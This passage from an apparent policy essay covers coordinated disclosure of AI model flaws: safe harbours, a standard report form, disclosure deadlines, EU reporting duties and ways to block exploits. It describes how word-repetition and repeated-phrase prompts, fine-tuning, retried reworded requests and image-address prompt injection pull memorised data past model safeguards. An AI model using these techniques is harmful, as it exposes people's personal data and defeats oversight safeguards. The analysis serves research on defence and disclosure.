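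Piao and colleagues found safe-harbour clauses in 67% of the 48 policies that mention AI and in 18% of the other 120. In total, about 54 of the 264 vendors, or one in five, have such a clause. The policies that mention AI also tend to be more complete in other ways, so their higher rate may reflect the vendors' experience with security researchers in general rather than a decision to protect people who test AI models.

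A safe harbour may not cover a researcher's work. Barton-Cooper and Gleave write that attempts to obtain harmful output breach developers' usage policies, and that safe harbours may not clearly apply because security programmes often exclude jailbreaks. Researchers whose work is out of scope may therefore get neither legal protection nor a reward.

HackerOne, a company that hosts reporting programmes, lists safe harbour for AI research separately from general safe harbour. Anthropic (2026) closed a disclosure programme there in May and moved reports to its public bug bounty. HackerOne's record for the closed programme marks the general protection as applying but leaves the AI entry empty. A researcher couldn't have relied on the AI protection, though the empty entry doesn't show that Anthropic refused it.

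A safe harbour is also one company's promise, so it can't bind anyone else. US copyright law gives some additional protection through exemptions for research on protected systems, but Longpre and colleagues describe these as limited. Researchers can reduce the uncertainty by asking for written permission before they start, as Carlini and colleagues did before they recovered the last layer of OpenAI's older models. However, this lets the company decide which research takes place.

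### One report for several recipients

*In-House Evaluation Is Not Enough* (Longpre, Klyman and colleagues, 2025) makes three proposals. Researchers should use a standard flaw report and follow agreed rules for testing. Developers should run disclosure programmes with a broad scope and a legal safe harbour. And the field needs a way to distribute reports to everyone a flaw affects. Longpre and Appel suggest a Disclosure Coordination Center for this, which would send each report to the relevant data suppliers, developers, model hosts, application companies and government agencies, and eventually release it to the public.

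FLARE-AI puts much of the first and third proposals into practice. Its developers began by comparing 12 reporting systems, including those of OpenAI, Anthropic, Google, CERT/CC and several public databases of AI incidents. The shortest form, OpenAI's security form, had 7 fields, and the longest, MITRE's form for attacks on AI systems, had 53. Only three systems allowed anonymous reports: CERT/CC's, the AI Incident Database's and a form that Anthropic has since replaced.

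Longer forms didn't always collect what developers needed. To reproduce a problem, a developer has to know the model, its version, and whether the reporter used the website, the programming interface or another company's product. Most reporting systems had a field for the model's name but left the rest to free text. Only the CERT/CC and Google forms included a question about whether the reporter had published the finding or was about to, although recipients said this information was critical for setting priorities.

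The designers consulted 49 people from 32 organisations and found a conflict. Reporters wanted a short form, while recipients wanted enough detail to act on. FLARE-AI's compromise has six required fields and up to 30 in all, and it works as follows:

1. The reporter answers three yes-or-no questions. These establish whether the flaw has already caused harm, whether someone could use it maliciously, and whether it involves child sexual abuse material. If it does, the form stops and directs the reporter to the proper authorities, because even possessing the evidence may be illegal.
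2. The other answers determine which further questions appear. A reporter describing a harmless-looking error, for example, doesn't have to fill in fields about attackers.
3. The website produces a report that software can read. The reporter can download it and send it privately, without the website storing a copy.
4. If the reporter wants help with distribution, the website suggests recipients based on the model and the type of flaw. These can include developers, CERT/CC and incident databases. The reporter chooses among them, and the website sends the report through an automatic connection or an official email address.

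This saves the reporter from filling in the same details on several forms, but nobody has yet shown that it leads to more reports or faster repairs. The evidence so far comes from sessions in which security researchers used early versions to report flaws they had already found. Easy distribution is also risky, because one click could send a working exploit to a dozen organisations, and carelessness at any one of them could break the embargo. The designers acknowledge that attackers might target a central store of reports, which is one reason the website doesn't keep them by default.

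A standard form doesn't guarantee a clear report. The designers' own example, a report on Carlini and colleagues' recovery of model weights, lists only GPT-3.5-Turbo as the affected system, but its description is about two older models, ada and babbage. An engineer who searched the reports for babbage would find this one only if the search covered descriptions. The report also records that the flaw had caused real-world harm, although the researchers had OpenAI's permission and saw no immediate practical consequences.

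### A report on the word-repetition attack

The sample report below applies these ideas to ChatGPT, using results that Nasr and colleagues later published. The wording is illustrative. The report lists the exploit and each suspected vulnerability as separate entries, so that a developer can close one entry without closing the others.

| Entry | Content |
|---|---|
| Summary | Anyone with an account can make the model output real people's contact details from its training data. |
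| System and route | gpt-3.5-turbo, through OpenAI's programming interface. The reporter adds the exact version, settings and test dates. |
| Exploit | Ask the model to repeat a single-token word, such as "poem", forever. After several hundred repetitions it produces other text, some of which matches web pages word for word. |
| Suspected vulnerability A | The model has memorised sensitive passages. Confidence: high, because outputs match existing text for at least 50 consecutive tokens. |
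| Suspected vulnerability B | Long repetition makes the model diverge from its chat behaviour. Confidence: high that this happens, low about why. |
| Affected versions | Confirmed: the version named above. Exploit failed: GPT-4, which may still have vulnerability A. Unknown: later versions and other routes of access. |
| Success rate | Divergence: almost every attempt. Memorised text: nearly 3% of output tokens. Memorised personal information: 16.9% of outputs tested. Cost: $200 for over 10,000 passages. |
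| Likely variants | Other single-token words (confirmed). Other prompts that cause divergence (untested). Fine-tuning that reverses the chat training (untested). |
| Evidence | Prompts, a script that runs the attack, redacted outputs, and the matching web pages. |
| Other recipients | Names of any other developers or coordinators who have the report, and the reporter's plans for publication. |

A report needs more than one figure for the success rate because "success" could mean several things. Longpre and Appel recommend that reports about a model's output state how often the bad output appears for relevant prompts. OpenAI's 50% threshold applies only to hijacked agents, but it shows why the choice of measure matters. Word repetition would easily meet that threshold if success meant divergence, but not if it meant that a given output contained personal information. The cost of each memorised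 passage, about two cents here, describes the danger better than either rate, because an attacker can run the prompt thousands of times and keep the useful outputs.

The entry on affected versions distinguishes a failed exploit from the absence of a vulnerability. A report that listed GPT-4 as "not affected" would have been wrong, as the later fine-tuning attack showed. The prediction about fine-tuning benefits from hindsight, but a reporter in 2023 could reasonably have guessed that other ways of undoing the chat training would release the same passages. Such a guess is useful to the developer as long as the report labels it as a guess.

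The evidence contains other people's personal details, such as phone numbers. The developer needs enough of the evidence to confirm the match, but those details don't need to be in a public database. A reporter who uses a service like FLARE-AI to send the report to both should redact the attachment and offer the full outputs to the developer separately.

If OpenAI then added a filter for repeated words, its engineers could mark the exploit as blocked. Vulnerability A would stay open until they had dealt with the memorised passages, and B until they had corrected the divergence or shown that it no longer mattered. If the report had instead been titled "ChatGPT leaks data when asked to repeat 'poem'" and had a single status field, they would probably have closed it the day they added the filter.

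## Deciding when to publish and how much

A developer may close a report on the day it installs a filter, but the person who sent the report still has to decide when to tell the public. People who find vulnerabilities in ordinary software often set a fixed deadline of 90 days. That works when the vendor can fix the product in time, which is far from certain for a weakness in a language model's weights.

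### The 90-day deadline

Project Zero, which Google created in 2014, popularized the disclosure deadline, according to Security Magazine's *Google announces Project Zero's full 90 day disclosure policy*. For over a decade before that, the team's researchers had let vendors decide when the details of a vulnerability could become public. Google Project Zero (2019) reports that many fixes took more than six months under that arrangement and some never arrived. The team therefore began telling vendors, in its first report of each vulnerability, that it would publish the details after 90 days.

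Most vendors met Project Zero's 90-day deadline. By July 2025 the team had applied it to 2,131 vulnerabilities and published only 95 of them without a fix. But 90 days was often tight. After complaints from Microsoft and Apple, described in ITPro's *Google's Project Zero bug reporting rules softened*, the team began in February 2015 to allow up to 14 more days to vendors who committed to a release date. Between then and July 2025, vendors used the extra days for about one vulnerability in eight.

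Project Zero has changed the rule several times:

| From | Rule |
|---|---|
| 2014 | The vendor has 90 days to release a fix |
| February 2015 | Up to 14 more days if the vendor commits to a release date |
| 2020 | Details on day 90, even if the vendor releases a fix sooner |
| 2021 | 90 days for the fix, then 30 days for users to install it |
| July 2025 | The same, plus an early announcement that a vulnerability exists |
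| November 2026 | Details on day 90, fixed or not, with no extra time |
| 2 February 2027 | Details on day 60 |
| 3 January 2028 | Details on day 30 |

The 30 extra days in Project Zero's 2021 rule were meant to give users time to install the fix (Willis, 2021). The early announcement, which Willis (2025) introduced as a trial, names the vendor, the product and the deadline but gives no technical details. For example, Google Project Zero's *Reporting Transparency* lists a report to Apple on 30 October 2026 about "macOS Frameworks", with a deadline of 28 January. Willis wanted to help companies that build on other companies' software, because they often integrate a fix long after the original vendor has finished it, and their users remain exposed until they do.

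All these rules assume that the vendor can make a fix and get it to users within the period. The vendor of a hosted language model can easily get a fix to users, but making one may take far longer than 90 days if it means retraining. If a model's weights are public, even a successful fix doesn't reach the copies that people have already downloaded.

The closest precedent comes from hardware. Project Zero waited 216 days before publishing Spectre and Meltdown, two groups of design flaws in processors, which manufacturers couldn't replace in every machine. But it made such exceptions in only ten of about 2,100 cases.

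### Two disclosures to OpenAI

Nasr and colleagues gave OpenAI the standard 90 days to deal with the word-repetition attack. Two security engineers at Dropbox, which uses OpenAI's models in its products, later reported a variant that OpenAI's first filter didn't catch. *Bye Bye Bye* (Breitenbach and Wood, 2024) describes how they made GPT-3.5 and GPT-4 output training data by repeating two-token phrases.

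| Step | Word repetition | Dropbox's variant |
|---|---|---|
| Odd behaviour first seen | 11 July 2023 | April 2023, with repeated characters |
| Training data found in the output | 31 July 2023 | January 2024 |
| Reported to OpenAI | 30 August 2023 | 24 January 2024 |
| Block observed | By 4 January 2024 | 29 January 2024 |
| Published | 28 November 2023 | 19 March 2024 |
| Time from report to publication | 90 days | 55 days |

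A 90-day embargo can leave users exposed for much longer than 90 days. Nasr and colleagues first saw strange output 140 days before they published. For the first 20 days they didn't know what it was, and they spent the next 30 preparing a draft for OpenAI. They also sent early drafts to the makers of the open models they had studied, including LLaMA and Mistral.

It isn't clear whether OpenAI had blocked the original attack by the time the paper came out. Breitenbach and Wood write in one place that OpenAI had begun filtering by then and in another that it added the filter afterwards. The first refusal they show dates from 4 January 2024. If the filter came later, anyone who read the paper in late November could have used the attack for a while, even though OpenAI had already known about it for three months.

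OpenAI blocked the variant much faster. It asked Dropbox to wait 90 days before publishing, but Breitenbach and Wood found the new prompts blocked after five days, and OpenAI let them publish early. A developer that already has a filter can extend it in days, so OpenAI needed far less than 90 days to block the prompts, but the memorised text was still in the weights when the embargo ended.

### When the vendor cannot fix the weakness

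Suppose a developer has blocked the known prompt by day 90 but says it can't remove the memorised text from its current model. Waiting for a fix could then delay publication indefinitely. Under its earlier policy, Project Zero published a report as soon as the vendor said it would not or could not repair the flaw. It marked the report "WontFix" and added its own assessment of the vendor's reply. A vendor who dismisses a report as harmless has little reason to object to publication, but the decision is harder when the vendor accepts that the problem is serious and has no way to fix it.

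One good reason to publish a weakness even when it has no fix is that users can often limit their own exposure. The Hacker News reports that the security company Striga disclosed two flaws in Ollama's Windows updater on 27 January 2026, and that the details came out after 90 days without a fix. Users could protect themselves by turning off automatic updates and removing Ollama from the list of programs that start at login. The public details also made it easier to check which versions were at risk. CERT Polska, the Polish response team that coordinated the disclosure, listed versions up to 0.17.5 as vulnerable, while Striga's co-founder said that every version up to 0.22.0 was.

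People whose phone numbers are in a model's weights can't protect themselves by changing a setting. But a company that knows models memorise text can keep customer records out of its fine-tuning data, and a developer can test its base model for memorised text before release.

Publication also lets other researchers study the weakness. Breitenbach and Wood had seen repeated text disrupt ChatGPT months before the paper appeared, but took the results for hallucinations. After the paper explained what some of the output might be, they found the gap in OpenAI's filter and told the company. An attacker could also have used the paper to find the gap, and wouldn't have reported it.

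Project Zero usually publishes code that demonstrates a vulnerability, because the code helps defenders recognise attacks and test repairs. It argues that this gives attackers little help, because a vulnerability in a browser, for example, is usually only one part of a complete attack. In its view, anyone skilled enough to build the rest could probably have found another way in. This argument doesn't apply well to prompts. A request to repeat a word forever is a complete attack, and a person with no technical skill can copy it into a chat window.

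The case for withholding a prompt that still works is stronger than the case for withholding most software exploits, but a short prompt is hard to describe without giving it away. Someone told only that "long repetition makes ChatGPT release training data" could reconstruct the attack in minutes. Saying less, for example that the model can release contact details it has memorised, would give other researchers almost nothing to work with.

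Secrecy also achieves less when other people find the same flaw independently. Outsiders noticed ChatGPT's odd behaviour in August 2023, before OpenAI had received any report. Dropbox published its findings on repeated characters that summer and presented them at a conference in the autumn, during the embargo on the word-repetition paper. By then, the way to make the model diverge was largely public. The embargo mainly kept secret that the output contained training data, though anyone who pasted a sentence of it into a search engine might have found out.

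On balance, the developer should get a short period to block the exploit, and the researcher should then publish both the weakness and the blocked prompt. The researcher can hold back variants that still work and should never publish other people's personal details. If the developer hasn't blocked the exploit by the deadline, the researcher should still publish the weakness, since users have gained nothing from the wait. Withholding the prompt longer makes sense only if nobody else seems to have found it.

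A block on one company's service protects only that service's users. Breitenbach and Wood published their method with OpenAI's consent, along with a script for finding more phrases that work. They also warned that the attack transferred to popular open models, which OpenAI's filter didn't cover. A researcher who suspects that an attack transfers should consider the users of those other models when choosing a publication date, although no single developer can block a prompt on every computer that runs an open model.

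In 2022 the Zero Day Initiative, which buys vulnerabilities from researchers and reports them to vendors, stopped giving vendors another full period before disclosure when a variant got around an earlier patch. TechTarget's *Zero Day Initiative launches new bug disclosure timelines* (2022) reports that the limit, usually 120 days, fell to 30 days for the most urgent of these flaws, 60 for those where the patch gave some protection and 90 for less serious ones. The organisation's managers complained of "placebo" patches and said they had been paying for the same bugs more than once. A rule like this discourages vendors from blocking only the reported exploit, but it is less fair to a developer who has no known fix to apply.

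Project Zero has now dropped its separate policy on variants. It had struggled to decide whether a flaw was fixed, especially when the vendor's code wasn't public, and sometimes went back and forth with a vendor several times over one report. Vendors had also made the decision harder by trying measures such as temporarily disabling part of a program. Under the new policy, the team will still record whether there is a fix, but this won't change the publication date. This approach suits language models because outsiders usually can't tell a block from a fix, and a researcher can describe what the developer did without having to classify it.

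### The 2026 dispute over shorter deadlines

The new policy also reflects a wider argument about whether AI has made 90 days too long. Himanshu Anand, a security analyst at Cloudflare, made the case earlier in 2026, and The Decoder's *AI turns patches into working exploits in 30 minutes* summarises it. In his view, the 90-day deadline assumed that the finder was probably alone, that any other finder would be slow, that the vendor had a head start on the repair, and that attackers needed days or weeks to turn a released patch into an exploit. He gave examples to show that none of this is still true:

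- Anand reported a flaw that let customers of an online store complete purchases without paying. The store told him that he was the eleventh person to report it in six weeks.
- After the developers of React, a tool for building websites, published several security patches, he used a language model to write a working exploit from them in 30 minutes. It could only stop a program from responding.
- A team used AI to find Copy Fail, a flaw that gave attackers full control of most Linux systems, with about an hour of scanning. Attackers were using it within days of its publication.
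- A week later, the finder of Dirty Frag, a similar Linux flaw, agreed a five-day embargo with the companies and projects that distribute Linux. Somebody else published the details within hours, before any of them had a patch ready.

These cases support different changes. The store is the best evidence for a shorter embargo, because ten other people already knew about the flaw and some might not have reported it. React is evidence against waiting to publish once a patch is out, since attackers can use the patch to find the flaw. The Copy Fail attacks followed publication, so they show how fast users must update, not how long a vendor should have to fix a flaw. Dirty Frag is the hardest to turn into a rule, because its embargo failed within hours and would have failed under a 30-day deadline too.

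Google's *Expanding Transparency* provides some broader evidence of rediscovery. It says that the company's reward programmes receive 15 times as many duplicate reports as in 2023. Part of the rise may simply reflect more reports overall, because the figure compares the number of duplicates rather than their share of all reports. It also covers people looking for rewards in Google's own products, and flaws deep inside other software may be harder to rediscover.

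Project Zero announced its schedule on 13 November 2026 and gave three reasons for it, according to Help Net Security's *Google Project Zero will disclose bugs after 90 days, fixed or not* (2026). Attackers are more likely to find a flaw during the embargo. They can also learn so much from a patch that the team now treats the time from patch to exploit as zero. And the team finds several vulnerabilities a week in products where it once found a few a year, so it no longer has time to negotiate over each one. It kept exceptions for flaws that attackers already exploit, for details that others have published, and for vendors who ask it to publish.

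Anthropic followed on 16 November with a shorter deadline for the vulnerabilities its Claude models find in other people's software. From 1 January 2027, vendors will have 30 days for high- and critical-severity flaws and 45 for the rest, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic Cuts Disclosure Deadline to 30 Days For Serious Bugs*. Anthropic will still wait 30 days after a patch before publishing full technical details. Anthropic's *Coordinated vulnerability disclosure* allows a 14-day extension for vendors who are making progress.

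The two policies treat severity differently. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Project Zero to Cut Disclosure Deadline to 30 Days by 2028* explains that Project Zero uses the same deadline for every flaw because serious flaws are no easier for attackers to find than minor ones. That is true, but the expected harm depends on what an attacker can do with a flaw as well as on the chance of finding it. A vendor with 20 reports and time to fix ten should start with the most serious, and Anthropic's deadlines encourage this.

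Vendors told Project Zero that a sudden change would expose unfixed flaws while they were still improving their processes. They also warned that they might have to fix the flaws it reported before more serious ones, and that some vendors might give up. The researcher Marcus Hutchins similarly said that maintainers would eventually "burn out and give up", in ITPro's *Companies will be given 30-day patch deadlines*. The same article cites the company VulnCheck, which counted 100,000 vulnerabilities discovered in 2026, more than double the total for 2025.

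Anthropic's own records support the objection. By 2 November 2026, Anthropic had reported 5,087 vulnerabilities to 680 open-source projects and knew of patches for 629, or about 12%. Some of those reports were probably recent, and Anthropic may not know of every patch. Even so, maintainers are clearly not keeping up. Anthropic acknowledged this when it announced the new deadline and gave them another 30 days for serious flaws that had already passed the old one.

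The PHP flaws give some support to each side. A 60-day deadline would have made their details public 11 days before users could update, and more time allowed a better repair. But two teams already knew the cause, and more time also meant more chances for a leak. Details did leak despite the embargo.

OpenAI has taken nearly the opposite position on flaws it finds in other companies' software. Its *Scaling coordinated vulnerability disclosure* (2025) leaves the timeline open by default, because the company expected its models to find more complex bugs that would take longer to repair. OpenAI reserves the right to publish when that is in the public interest. An open timeline gives a careful maintainer time to repair the flaw properly, but Project Zero abandoned open timelines after years of slow repairs.

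The case for publishing soon after a patch is stronger than the case for allowing only 30 days to write one. Attackers can read a patch immediately, but a shorter deadline doesn't give a maintainer more working hours each day. Project Zero argues that vendors can protect users in other ways while they work on the fix, so a 30-day deadline will often be a deadline for blocking the attack rather than fixing the flaw. This seems reasonable for a hosted language model, given that OpenAI blocked Dropbox's variant in five days. Retraining a model may take longer than 90 days, so the choice between 30 and 90 days matters much less for the fix.

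### What EU law requires

Private deadlines bind only those who adopt them. EU law requires companies, but not the researchers who find the flaws, to report some problems to the authorities.

Since 11 September 2026, the Cyber Resilience Act has required manufacturers of "products with digital elements", which include software, to report actively exploited vulnerabilities. According to *Policy Pulse*, a manufacturer must send an early warning within 24 hours, a fuller notification within 72 hours, and a final report 14 days after a corrective measure becomes available. The Act's wording is "corrective or mitigating measure", so a block may be enough to start the 14 days. The duty also covers products that were on the market before it took effect.

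Under the Act, this duty applies only if there is reliable evidence that a malicious actor has exploited the vulnerability in a system without its owner's permission. A researcher's demonstration of an exploit, like the one Nasr and colleagues sent to OpenAI, wouldn't count. If criminals used the same attack to collect phone numbers and the manufacturer had reliable evidence of it, the duty could apply. The manufacturer would then also have to inform affected users and tell them about anything they could do to protect themselves.

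Whether the Act covers a hosted model depends on how people access it. The Act covers processing on the manufacturer's computers if a product needs that processing to perform one of its functions. A phone chat app can't work without its model, so the two probably count as one product. A model that customers reach only through a programming interface probably falls outside the Act, because the customer has no product for the model to support. The same weakness in the same weights could therefore be reportable when the model is offered through an app but not when it is offered only through a programming interface.

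The AI Act applies to models more directly. Developers of general-purpose models that pose "systemic risk", broadly the most capable ones, must report serious incidents and possible corrective measures to the EU's AI Office without undue delay. This covers both hosted models and those with public weights. A separate article sets a general limit of 15 days for reporting serious incidents involving high-risk systems, such as software that ranks job applicants, once the rules for those systems apply.

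Harm triggers the AI Act's duties. A serious incident is one that leads to death or serious damage to health, serious and irreversible disruption of critical infrastructure, serious damage to property or the environment, or a breach of EU laws that protect fundamental rights. Such an incident can happen without an attacker, so a model's release of someone's private details in response to an innocent question might qualify if it broke data protection law. A memorised phone number that nobody has extracted would not qualify, even if the developer knew it was there.

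## Blocking a known exploit

A developer who receives a working exploit usually blocks it before looking for a fix. The developer of a hosted model can choose between several kinds of block, which miss different attacks and disrupt legitimate users in different ways.

| Block | Time to deploy | Legitimate use it can harm | What it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Input filter: rejects prompts that resemble the attack | Days, or less if a filter already exists | Harmless prompts of the same form | Prompts of another form that have the same effect |
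| Output filter: stops replies that match the training data | Longer at first, because the developer has to index the training data | Quotations, software licences, standard code | Near-copies, and matches that are too short |
| Refusal training: teaches the model to decline the request | Longer than an input filter, because the developer has to train and test a new version | Innocent requests that resemble the attack | Rewordings that the training didn't cover; fine-tuning that undoes it |
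| Rate limits and account suspensions | Almost immediate if the controls exist | Bulk customers and researchers | Attacks that need few requests or use many accounts |
| Withdrawal of a feature | Quick to switch off, but customers need time to adapt | Everything customers used the feature for | Attacks that don't need the feature |

### OpenAI's repetition filters

When the word-repetition paper came out in November 2023, the attack already failed on some services. 404 Media's *Google Researchers' Attack Convinces ChatGPT to Reveal Its Training Data* reports that ChatGPT refused the outlet's request to repeat "poem". *Research team exploits ChatGPT vulnerability to extract training data*, from the technology site The Decoder, describes mixed results from a reporter's tests. Through OpenAI's programming interface, GPT-3.5 repeated the word endlessly without producing any other text, and GPT-4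 blocked the attack. Through Microsoft's Azure cloud, GPT-3.5 still stopped repeating the word and produced random text, though the reporter couldn't confirm that any of it was training data. The block on OpenAI's interface apparently didn't extend to Azure.

Within days, ChatGPT was showing a warning that requests to repeat a word forever violated its terms and content policy, according to 404 Media's *Asking ChatGPT to Repeat Words 'Forever' Is Now a Terms of Service Violation*. The Ukrainian site Mezha.Media adds that ChatGPT repeated the word "computer" several dozen times before the warning appeared. This suggests that OpenAI was checking the reply, and perhaps also the prompt.

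The block also stopped harmless requests. In *ChatGPT will take serious offense if you ask it to repeat a word*, Chakravarti (2023) asked for the word "dog" 505 times and got an error message. Few people need that, so the block did little harm. But OpenAI's published rules didn't mention repetition, so users who got the warning couldn't look up what they had done wrong.

By early January 2024, OpenAI's programming interface was also refusing prompts that contained many copies of a single token. This filter closely matched the published attack. The 2023 paper had reported that words of several tokens didn't work, but its prompts had left most of the repeating to the model. Breitenbach and Wood, the Dropbox engineers, instead put thousands of copies of a two-token phrase in the prompt, and the filter didn't block them.

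Prompting GPT-3.5 with about 2,000 copies of one phrase made it output sentences from the public documentation of a programming tool. Four sentences matched the documentation for 11, 43, 21 and 37 tokens. These matches are too short to pass the 50-token test that Nasr and colleagues used, but together they leave little doubt about where the text came from. Prompting GPT-4 with 12,000 copies of another phrase produced twelve verses of Genesis, in nearly the wording of one English translation. The engineers couldn't get that version by asking GPT-4 to quote one of the verses in every translation it knew. The attack didn't produce the passage every time, but it worked on a model that resisted the original attack.

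OpenAI then widened the filter to cover repeated phrases of several tokens. It also limited how long its servers would spend on one request, after Dropbox found that asking GPT-4 to repeat a two-word phrase forever could occupy a server for at least ten minutes. OpenAI didn't confirm that this was a bug. A time limit applies whatever the prompt says, so it should also hinder unknown attacks that need very long replies. But Dropbox's attacks put the repetition in the prompt, so they didn't need a long reply.

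Even the wider filter recognises an attack only by its repetition, so it would miss both the cluster attack and the fine-tuning attack.

### Output filters and near-copies

An output filter compares the model's reply with its training data without using the prompt, so in principle it can stop memorised text whichever attack draws it out. In 2022, GitHub's programming assistant Copilot offered such a filter, which withheld suggestions that matched about 150 characters of public code.

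Ippolito, Tramèr and colleagues (2022), in *Preventing Generation of Verbatim Memorization in Language Models Gives a False Sense of Privacy*, found several ways past Copilot's filter. When they gave Copilot the opening of a well-known function from the video game *Quake*, the filter blocked the rest. When they presented the opening as comments in another programming language, Copilot produced the whole function as comments. When they gave the variables French names, Copilot continued the function with French names. Memorised text also sometimes passed the filter without such prompting, because Copilot had changed its capitalisation or spacing or made a small mistake.

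GitHub hadn't published the details of its filter, so the researchers built and studied a stricter one, called MemFree. Before the model adds a token, MemFree checks whether that token would complete a ten-token sequence from the training data. If it would, MemFree rules the token out and the model chooses another. To make the check fast, the researchers used a Bloom filter, a compact index that never misses a sequence stored in it but occasionally reports one that isn't there. The index for 800 gigabytes of training text took up 1.6 gigabytes.

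A simplified example shows why this isn't enough. Suppose that each word is one token and that the training data contains this sentence:

```
For press enquiries please call our spokeswoman Jane Smith on 555 0100
```

The model reproduces the first nine words. The tenth, "on", would complete a forbidden sequence, so MemFree rules it out. The model takes its next most likely choice, which could well be "at", and then continues from memory:

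```
For press enquiries please call our spokeswoman Jane Smith at 555 0100
```

The filter has worked as designed, because no ten-word sequence in the new sentence matches the original, but the new sentence still contains the phone number.

Ippolito and colleagues tested MemFree on GPT-Neo, a family of open models. The filter made the output less similar to the training data on average, especially for passages that occurred many times in the data. But some output was still close enough to the original that a person would have considered it copied. In a separate test without any filter, the researchers found up to twice as many memorised passages when they included near-copies. They caution that their similarity measure can count too many passages or too few. A filter based on it might therefore block a good deal of original text.

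MemFree can also miss personal data. In these experiments, its index held only sequences that occurred at least ten times in the training data, because models are most likely to memorise repeated text. The index could therefore leave out someone's phone number, which may occur only once. Indexing every sequence could close this gap. The full index would have taken 40.5 gigabytes, which a large company could easily store.

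The other gap is harder to close. A phone number is usually shorter than ten tokens and always far shorter than 150 characters, so either filter can miss one that appears on its own. If the developer shortens the minimum match, the filter blocks ordinary phrases. 404 Media's *Not Just David Mayer* describes a possible example of blocking very short strings, in which ChatGPT failed on ordinary questions about a few people, including the law professors Jonathan Zittrain and Jonathan Turley. OpenAI had not explained why when the article appeared. If the cause was a filter on names, it stopped every answer that mentioned these people, however harmless.

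Commercial models still produced long near-copies of books in 2025. Ahmed, Cooper and colleagues (2026), in *Extracting books from production language models*, gave four models the opening of a book and repeatedly asked for more. Keeping each instalment short helped them avoid output filters. Counting only near-verbatim passages of at least 100 words, they recovered 95.8% of the first *Harry Potter* novel from Claude 3.7 Sonnet, 76.8% from Gemini 2.5 Pro, 70.3% from Grok 3 and 4.0% from GPT-4.1. These are the best results for an unusually well-memorised book, and most of the experiments recovered 10% or less. The researchers also used different settings for each model, so the figures can't be used to rank the companies' safeguards.

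### Refusal training and usage limits

The same study gives some idea of how well refusals work. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Grok 3 continued the book when asked, but Claude 3.7 Sonnet and GPT-4.1 refused. Ahmed and colleagues then sent randomly altered versions of the request until one worked. For *Harry Potter*, this took 258 attempts with Claude and 5,179 with GPT-4.1. After one success, Claude produced nearly the whole book. GPT-4.1 refused to continue past the first chapter, which is why so little of the book came out.

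A very high refusal rate is weak protection against someone who can automate the attempts. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in *N* attempts is:

```
1 − (1 − p)^N
```

A model that refuses 4,999 requests in 5,000 has a *p* of 0.0002. An attacker who makes 5,000 attempts has a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

Rate limits help here by slowing repeated attempts. At 100 attempts a day, the 5,179 attempts against GPT-4.1 would have taken 52 days. Limits do less against word repetition, which yielded over 10,000 passages. If a limit had allowed the researchers only a hundredth of their queries, they would still have extracted roughly 100 passages. An attacker can also open more accounts. Suspending accounts for repetitive requests would also affect researchers who measure memorisation.

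One advantage of refusal training over a filter is that the refusals are part of the weights, so they apply wherever a company offers the new version of the model, including through another company's cloud. But the model has to learn to distinguish an attack from an innocent request, and the two can be identical. For example, a student may ask for the next page of a novel that has been out of copyright for a century. Customers can also remove the refusals by fine-tuning the model. Nasr and colleagues note that OpenAI had trained GPT-4 to refuse some requests related to training-data extraction, yet fine-tuning still made it release memorised text.

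### Withdrawing a feature

OpenAI could stop that attack by closing its fine-tuning service, but customers would lose a product they had paid for and built on. A filter on the examples that customers upload would be less drastic but hard to design, because the attack worked with 1,000 ordinary documents, none of which needed to look suspicious.

Companies often compromise by restricting a feature. ChatGPT used to display images from any web address. As in EchoLeak, an attacker's instructions could make it leak private information by putting it into an image's address. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, reports that OpenAI could have blocked all outside images but instead added a check on whether each image was "safe" to display, a choice he found "a bit weird". Blocking all outside images would have prevented this kind of leak however an attacker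 worded the instructions. The check lets users keep the feature, but their protection depends on OpenAI judging every address correctly.

A developer can also withdraw a whole model. Ahmed and colleagues told the four companies about their results in September 2025, and by the end of November Anthropic no longer offered Claude 3.7 Sonnet in its chat application. Companies routinely retire old models, so the report may not have been the reason. Retiring a model stops it from leaking text, but its successor may have memorised the same books. When the 90-day embargo ended in December, the extraction method still worked on some of the systems.

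### Rapid response

OpenAI's first filter fitted the published attack so closely that a near relative got past it. Peng, Michael and colleagues (2024), in *Rapid Response*, propose a way to block such relatives before anyone uses them. They designed it for jailbreaks, and several of them worked at Anthropic. In its most successful form, it has three steps:

1. The developer notices a jailbreak that worked. A language model summarises its strategy and then writes about 1,000 new prompts that apply the strategy to other harmful requests.
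2. The developer combines these with harmless prompts and trains an input filter, itself a language model, to tell them apart.
3. The developer adjusts the filter's threshold so that the system refuses about as many prompts as it did before.

The researchers tested this with six jailbreak strategies and three models. For each strategy, they also prepared a variant that the filter was not given. For example, one strategy disguised the request with a simple cipher, and its variant used Morse code. Given one example of each strategy, the filter reduced the success rate of attacks like those examples by 99.6% and that of the variants by 93.6%.

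They compared this with four other methods. In one, a language model wrote search patterns to match the text of known attacks. With one example of each strategy, these patterns reduced the success of familiar attacks more than fifteenfold, but they did much worse on the unseen variants. When the trained filter had no artificial examples to learn from, 12% of attacks succeeded on average across both kinds of test, compared with about 1.3% when the researchers generated the full number.

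The trained filter refused only slightly more harmless prompts than the original system. However, the harmless prompts used to train and test it came from the same collection of ChatGPT conversations, and the researchers acknowledge that this probably explains part of the result. A company whose customers ask different kinds of questions might see more wrongful refusals.

The 93.6% may also be optimistic, because the researchers fixed the variants in advance. Real attackers keep changing their prompts until something works, and Peng and colleagues warn that attackers who know about the method might design prompts to defeat it. The developer also has to notice the first attack. Peng and colleagues assume that the developer can recognise a successful jailbreak by examining the output afterwards, but outside researchers told OpenAI about word repetition.

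The study didn't test training-data extraction. A language model asked for variants of the word-repetition prompt might well have produced a prompt to repeat a phrase, which is the gap Dropbox found. It would have been much less likely to produce the fine-tuning attack, because that attack isn't a prompt.

Peng and colleagues add that the method suits attacks in which each success does little harm, because the developer then has time to react. If a single reply could do serious damage, rapid response alone may not be enough. Most leaks of memorised text are less serious, but if a model gives a stranger someone's home address, improving the filter later can't undo that.

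### When a block is taken for a fix

A block gives the developer time to look for a fix and makes determined attackers spend time and money, as the attempts against GPT-4.1 show. These are good reasons to block nearly every serious exploit as soon as possible. The exception is a minor leak that the developer could stop only by disabling something many people depend on.

The danger is that work stops once the exploit is blocked. *Extracting Training Data from ChatGPT*, a blog post about the word-repetition attack, says that people shown an exploit often make "whatever minimal change is necessary to stop that specific exploit". The complaint then goes away, and the engineers have other problems for which attacks still work.

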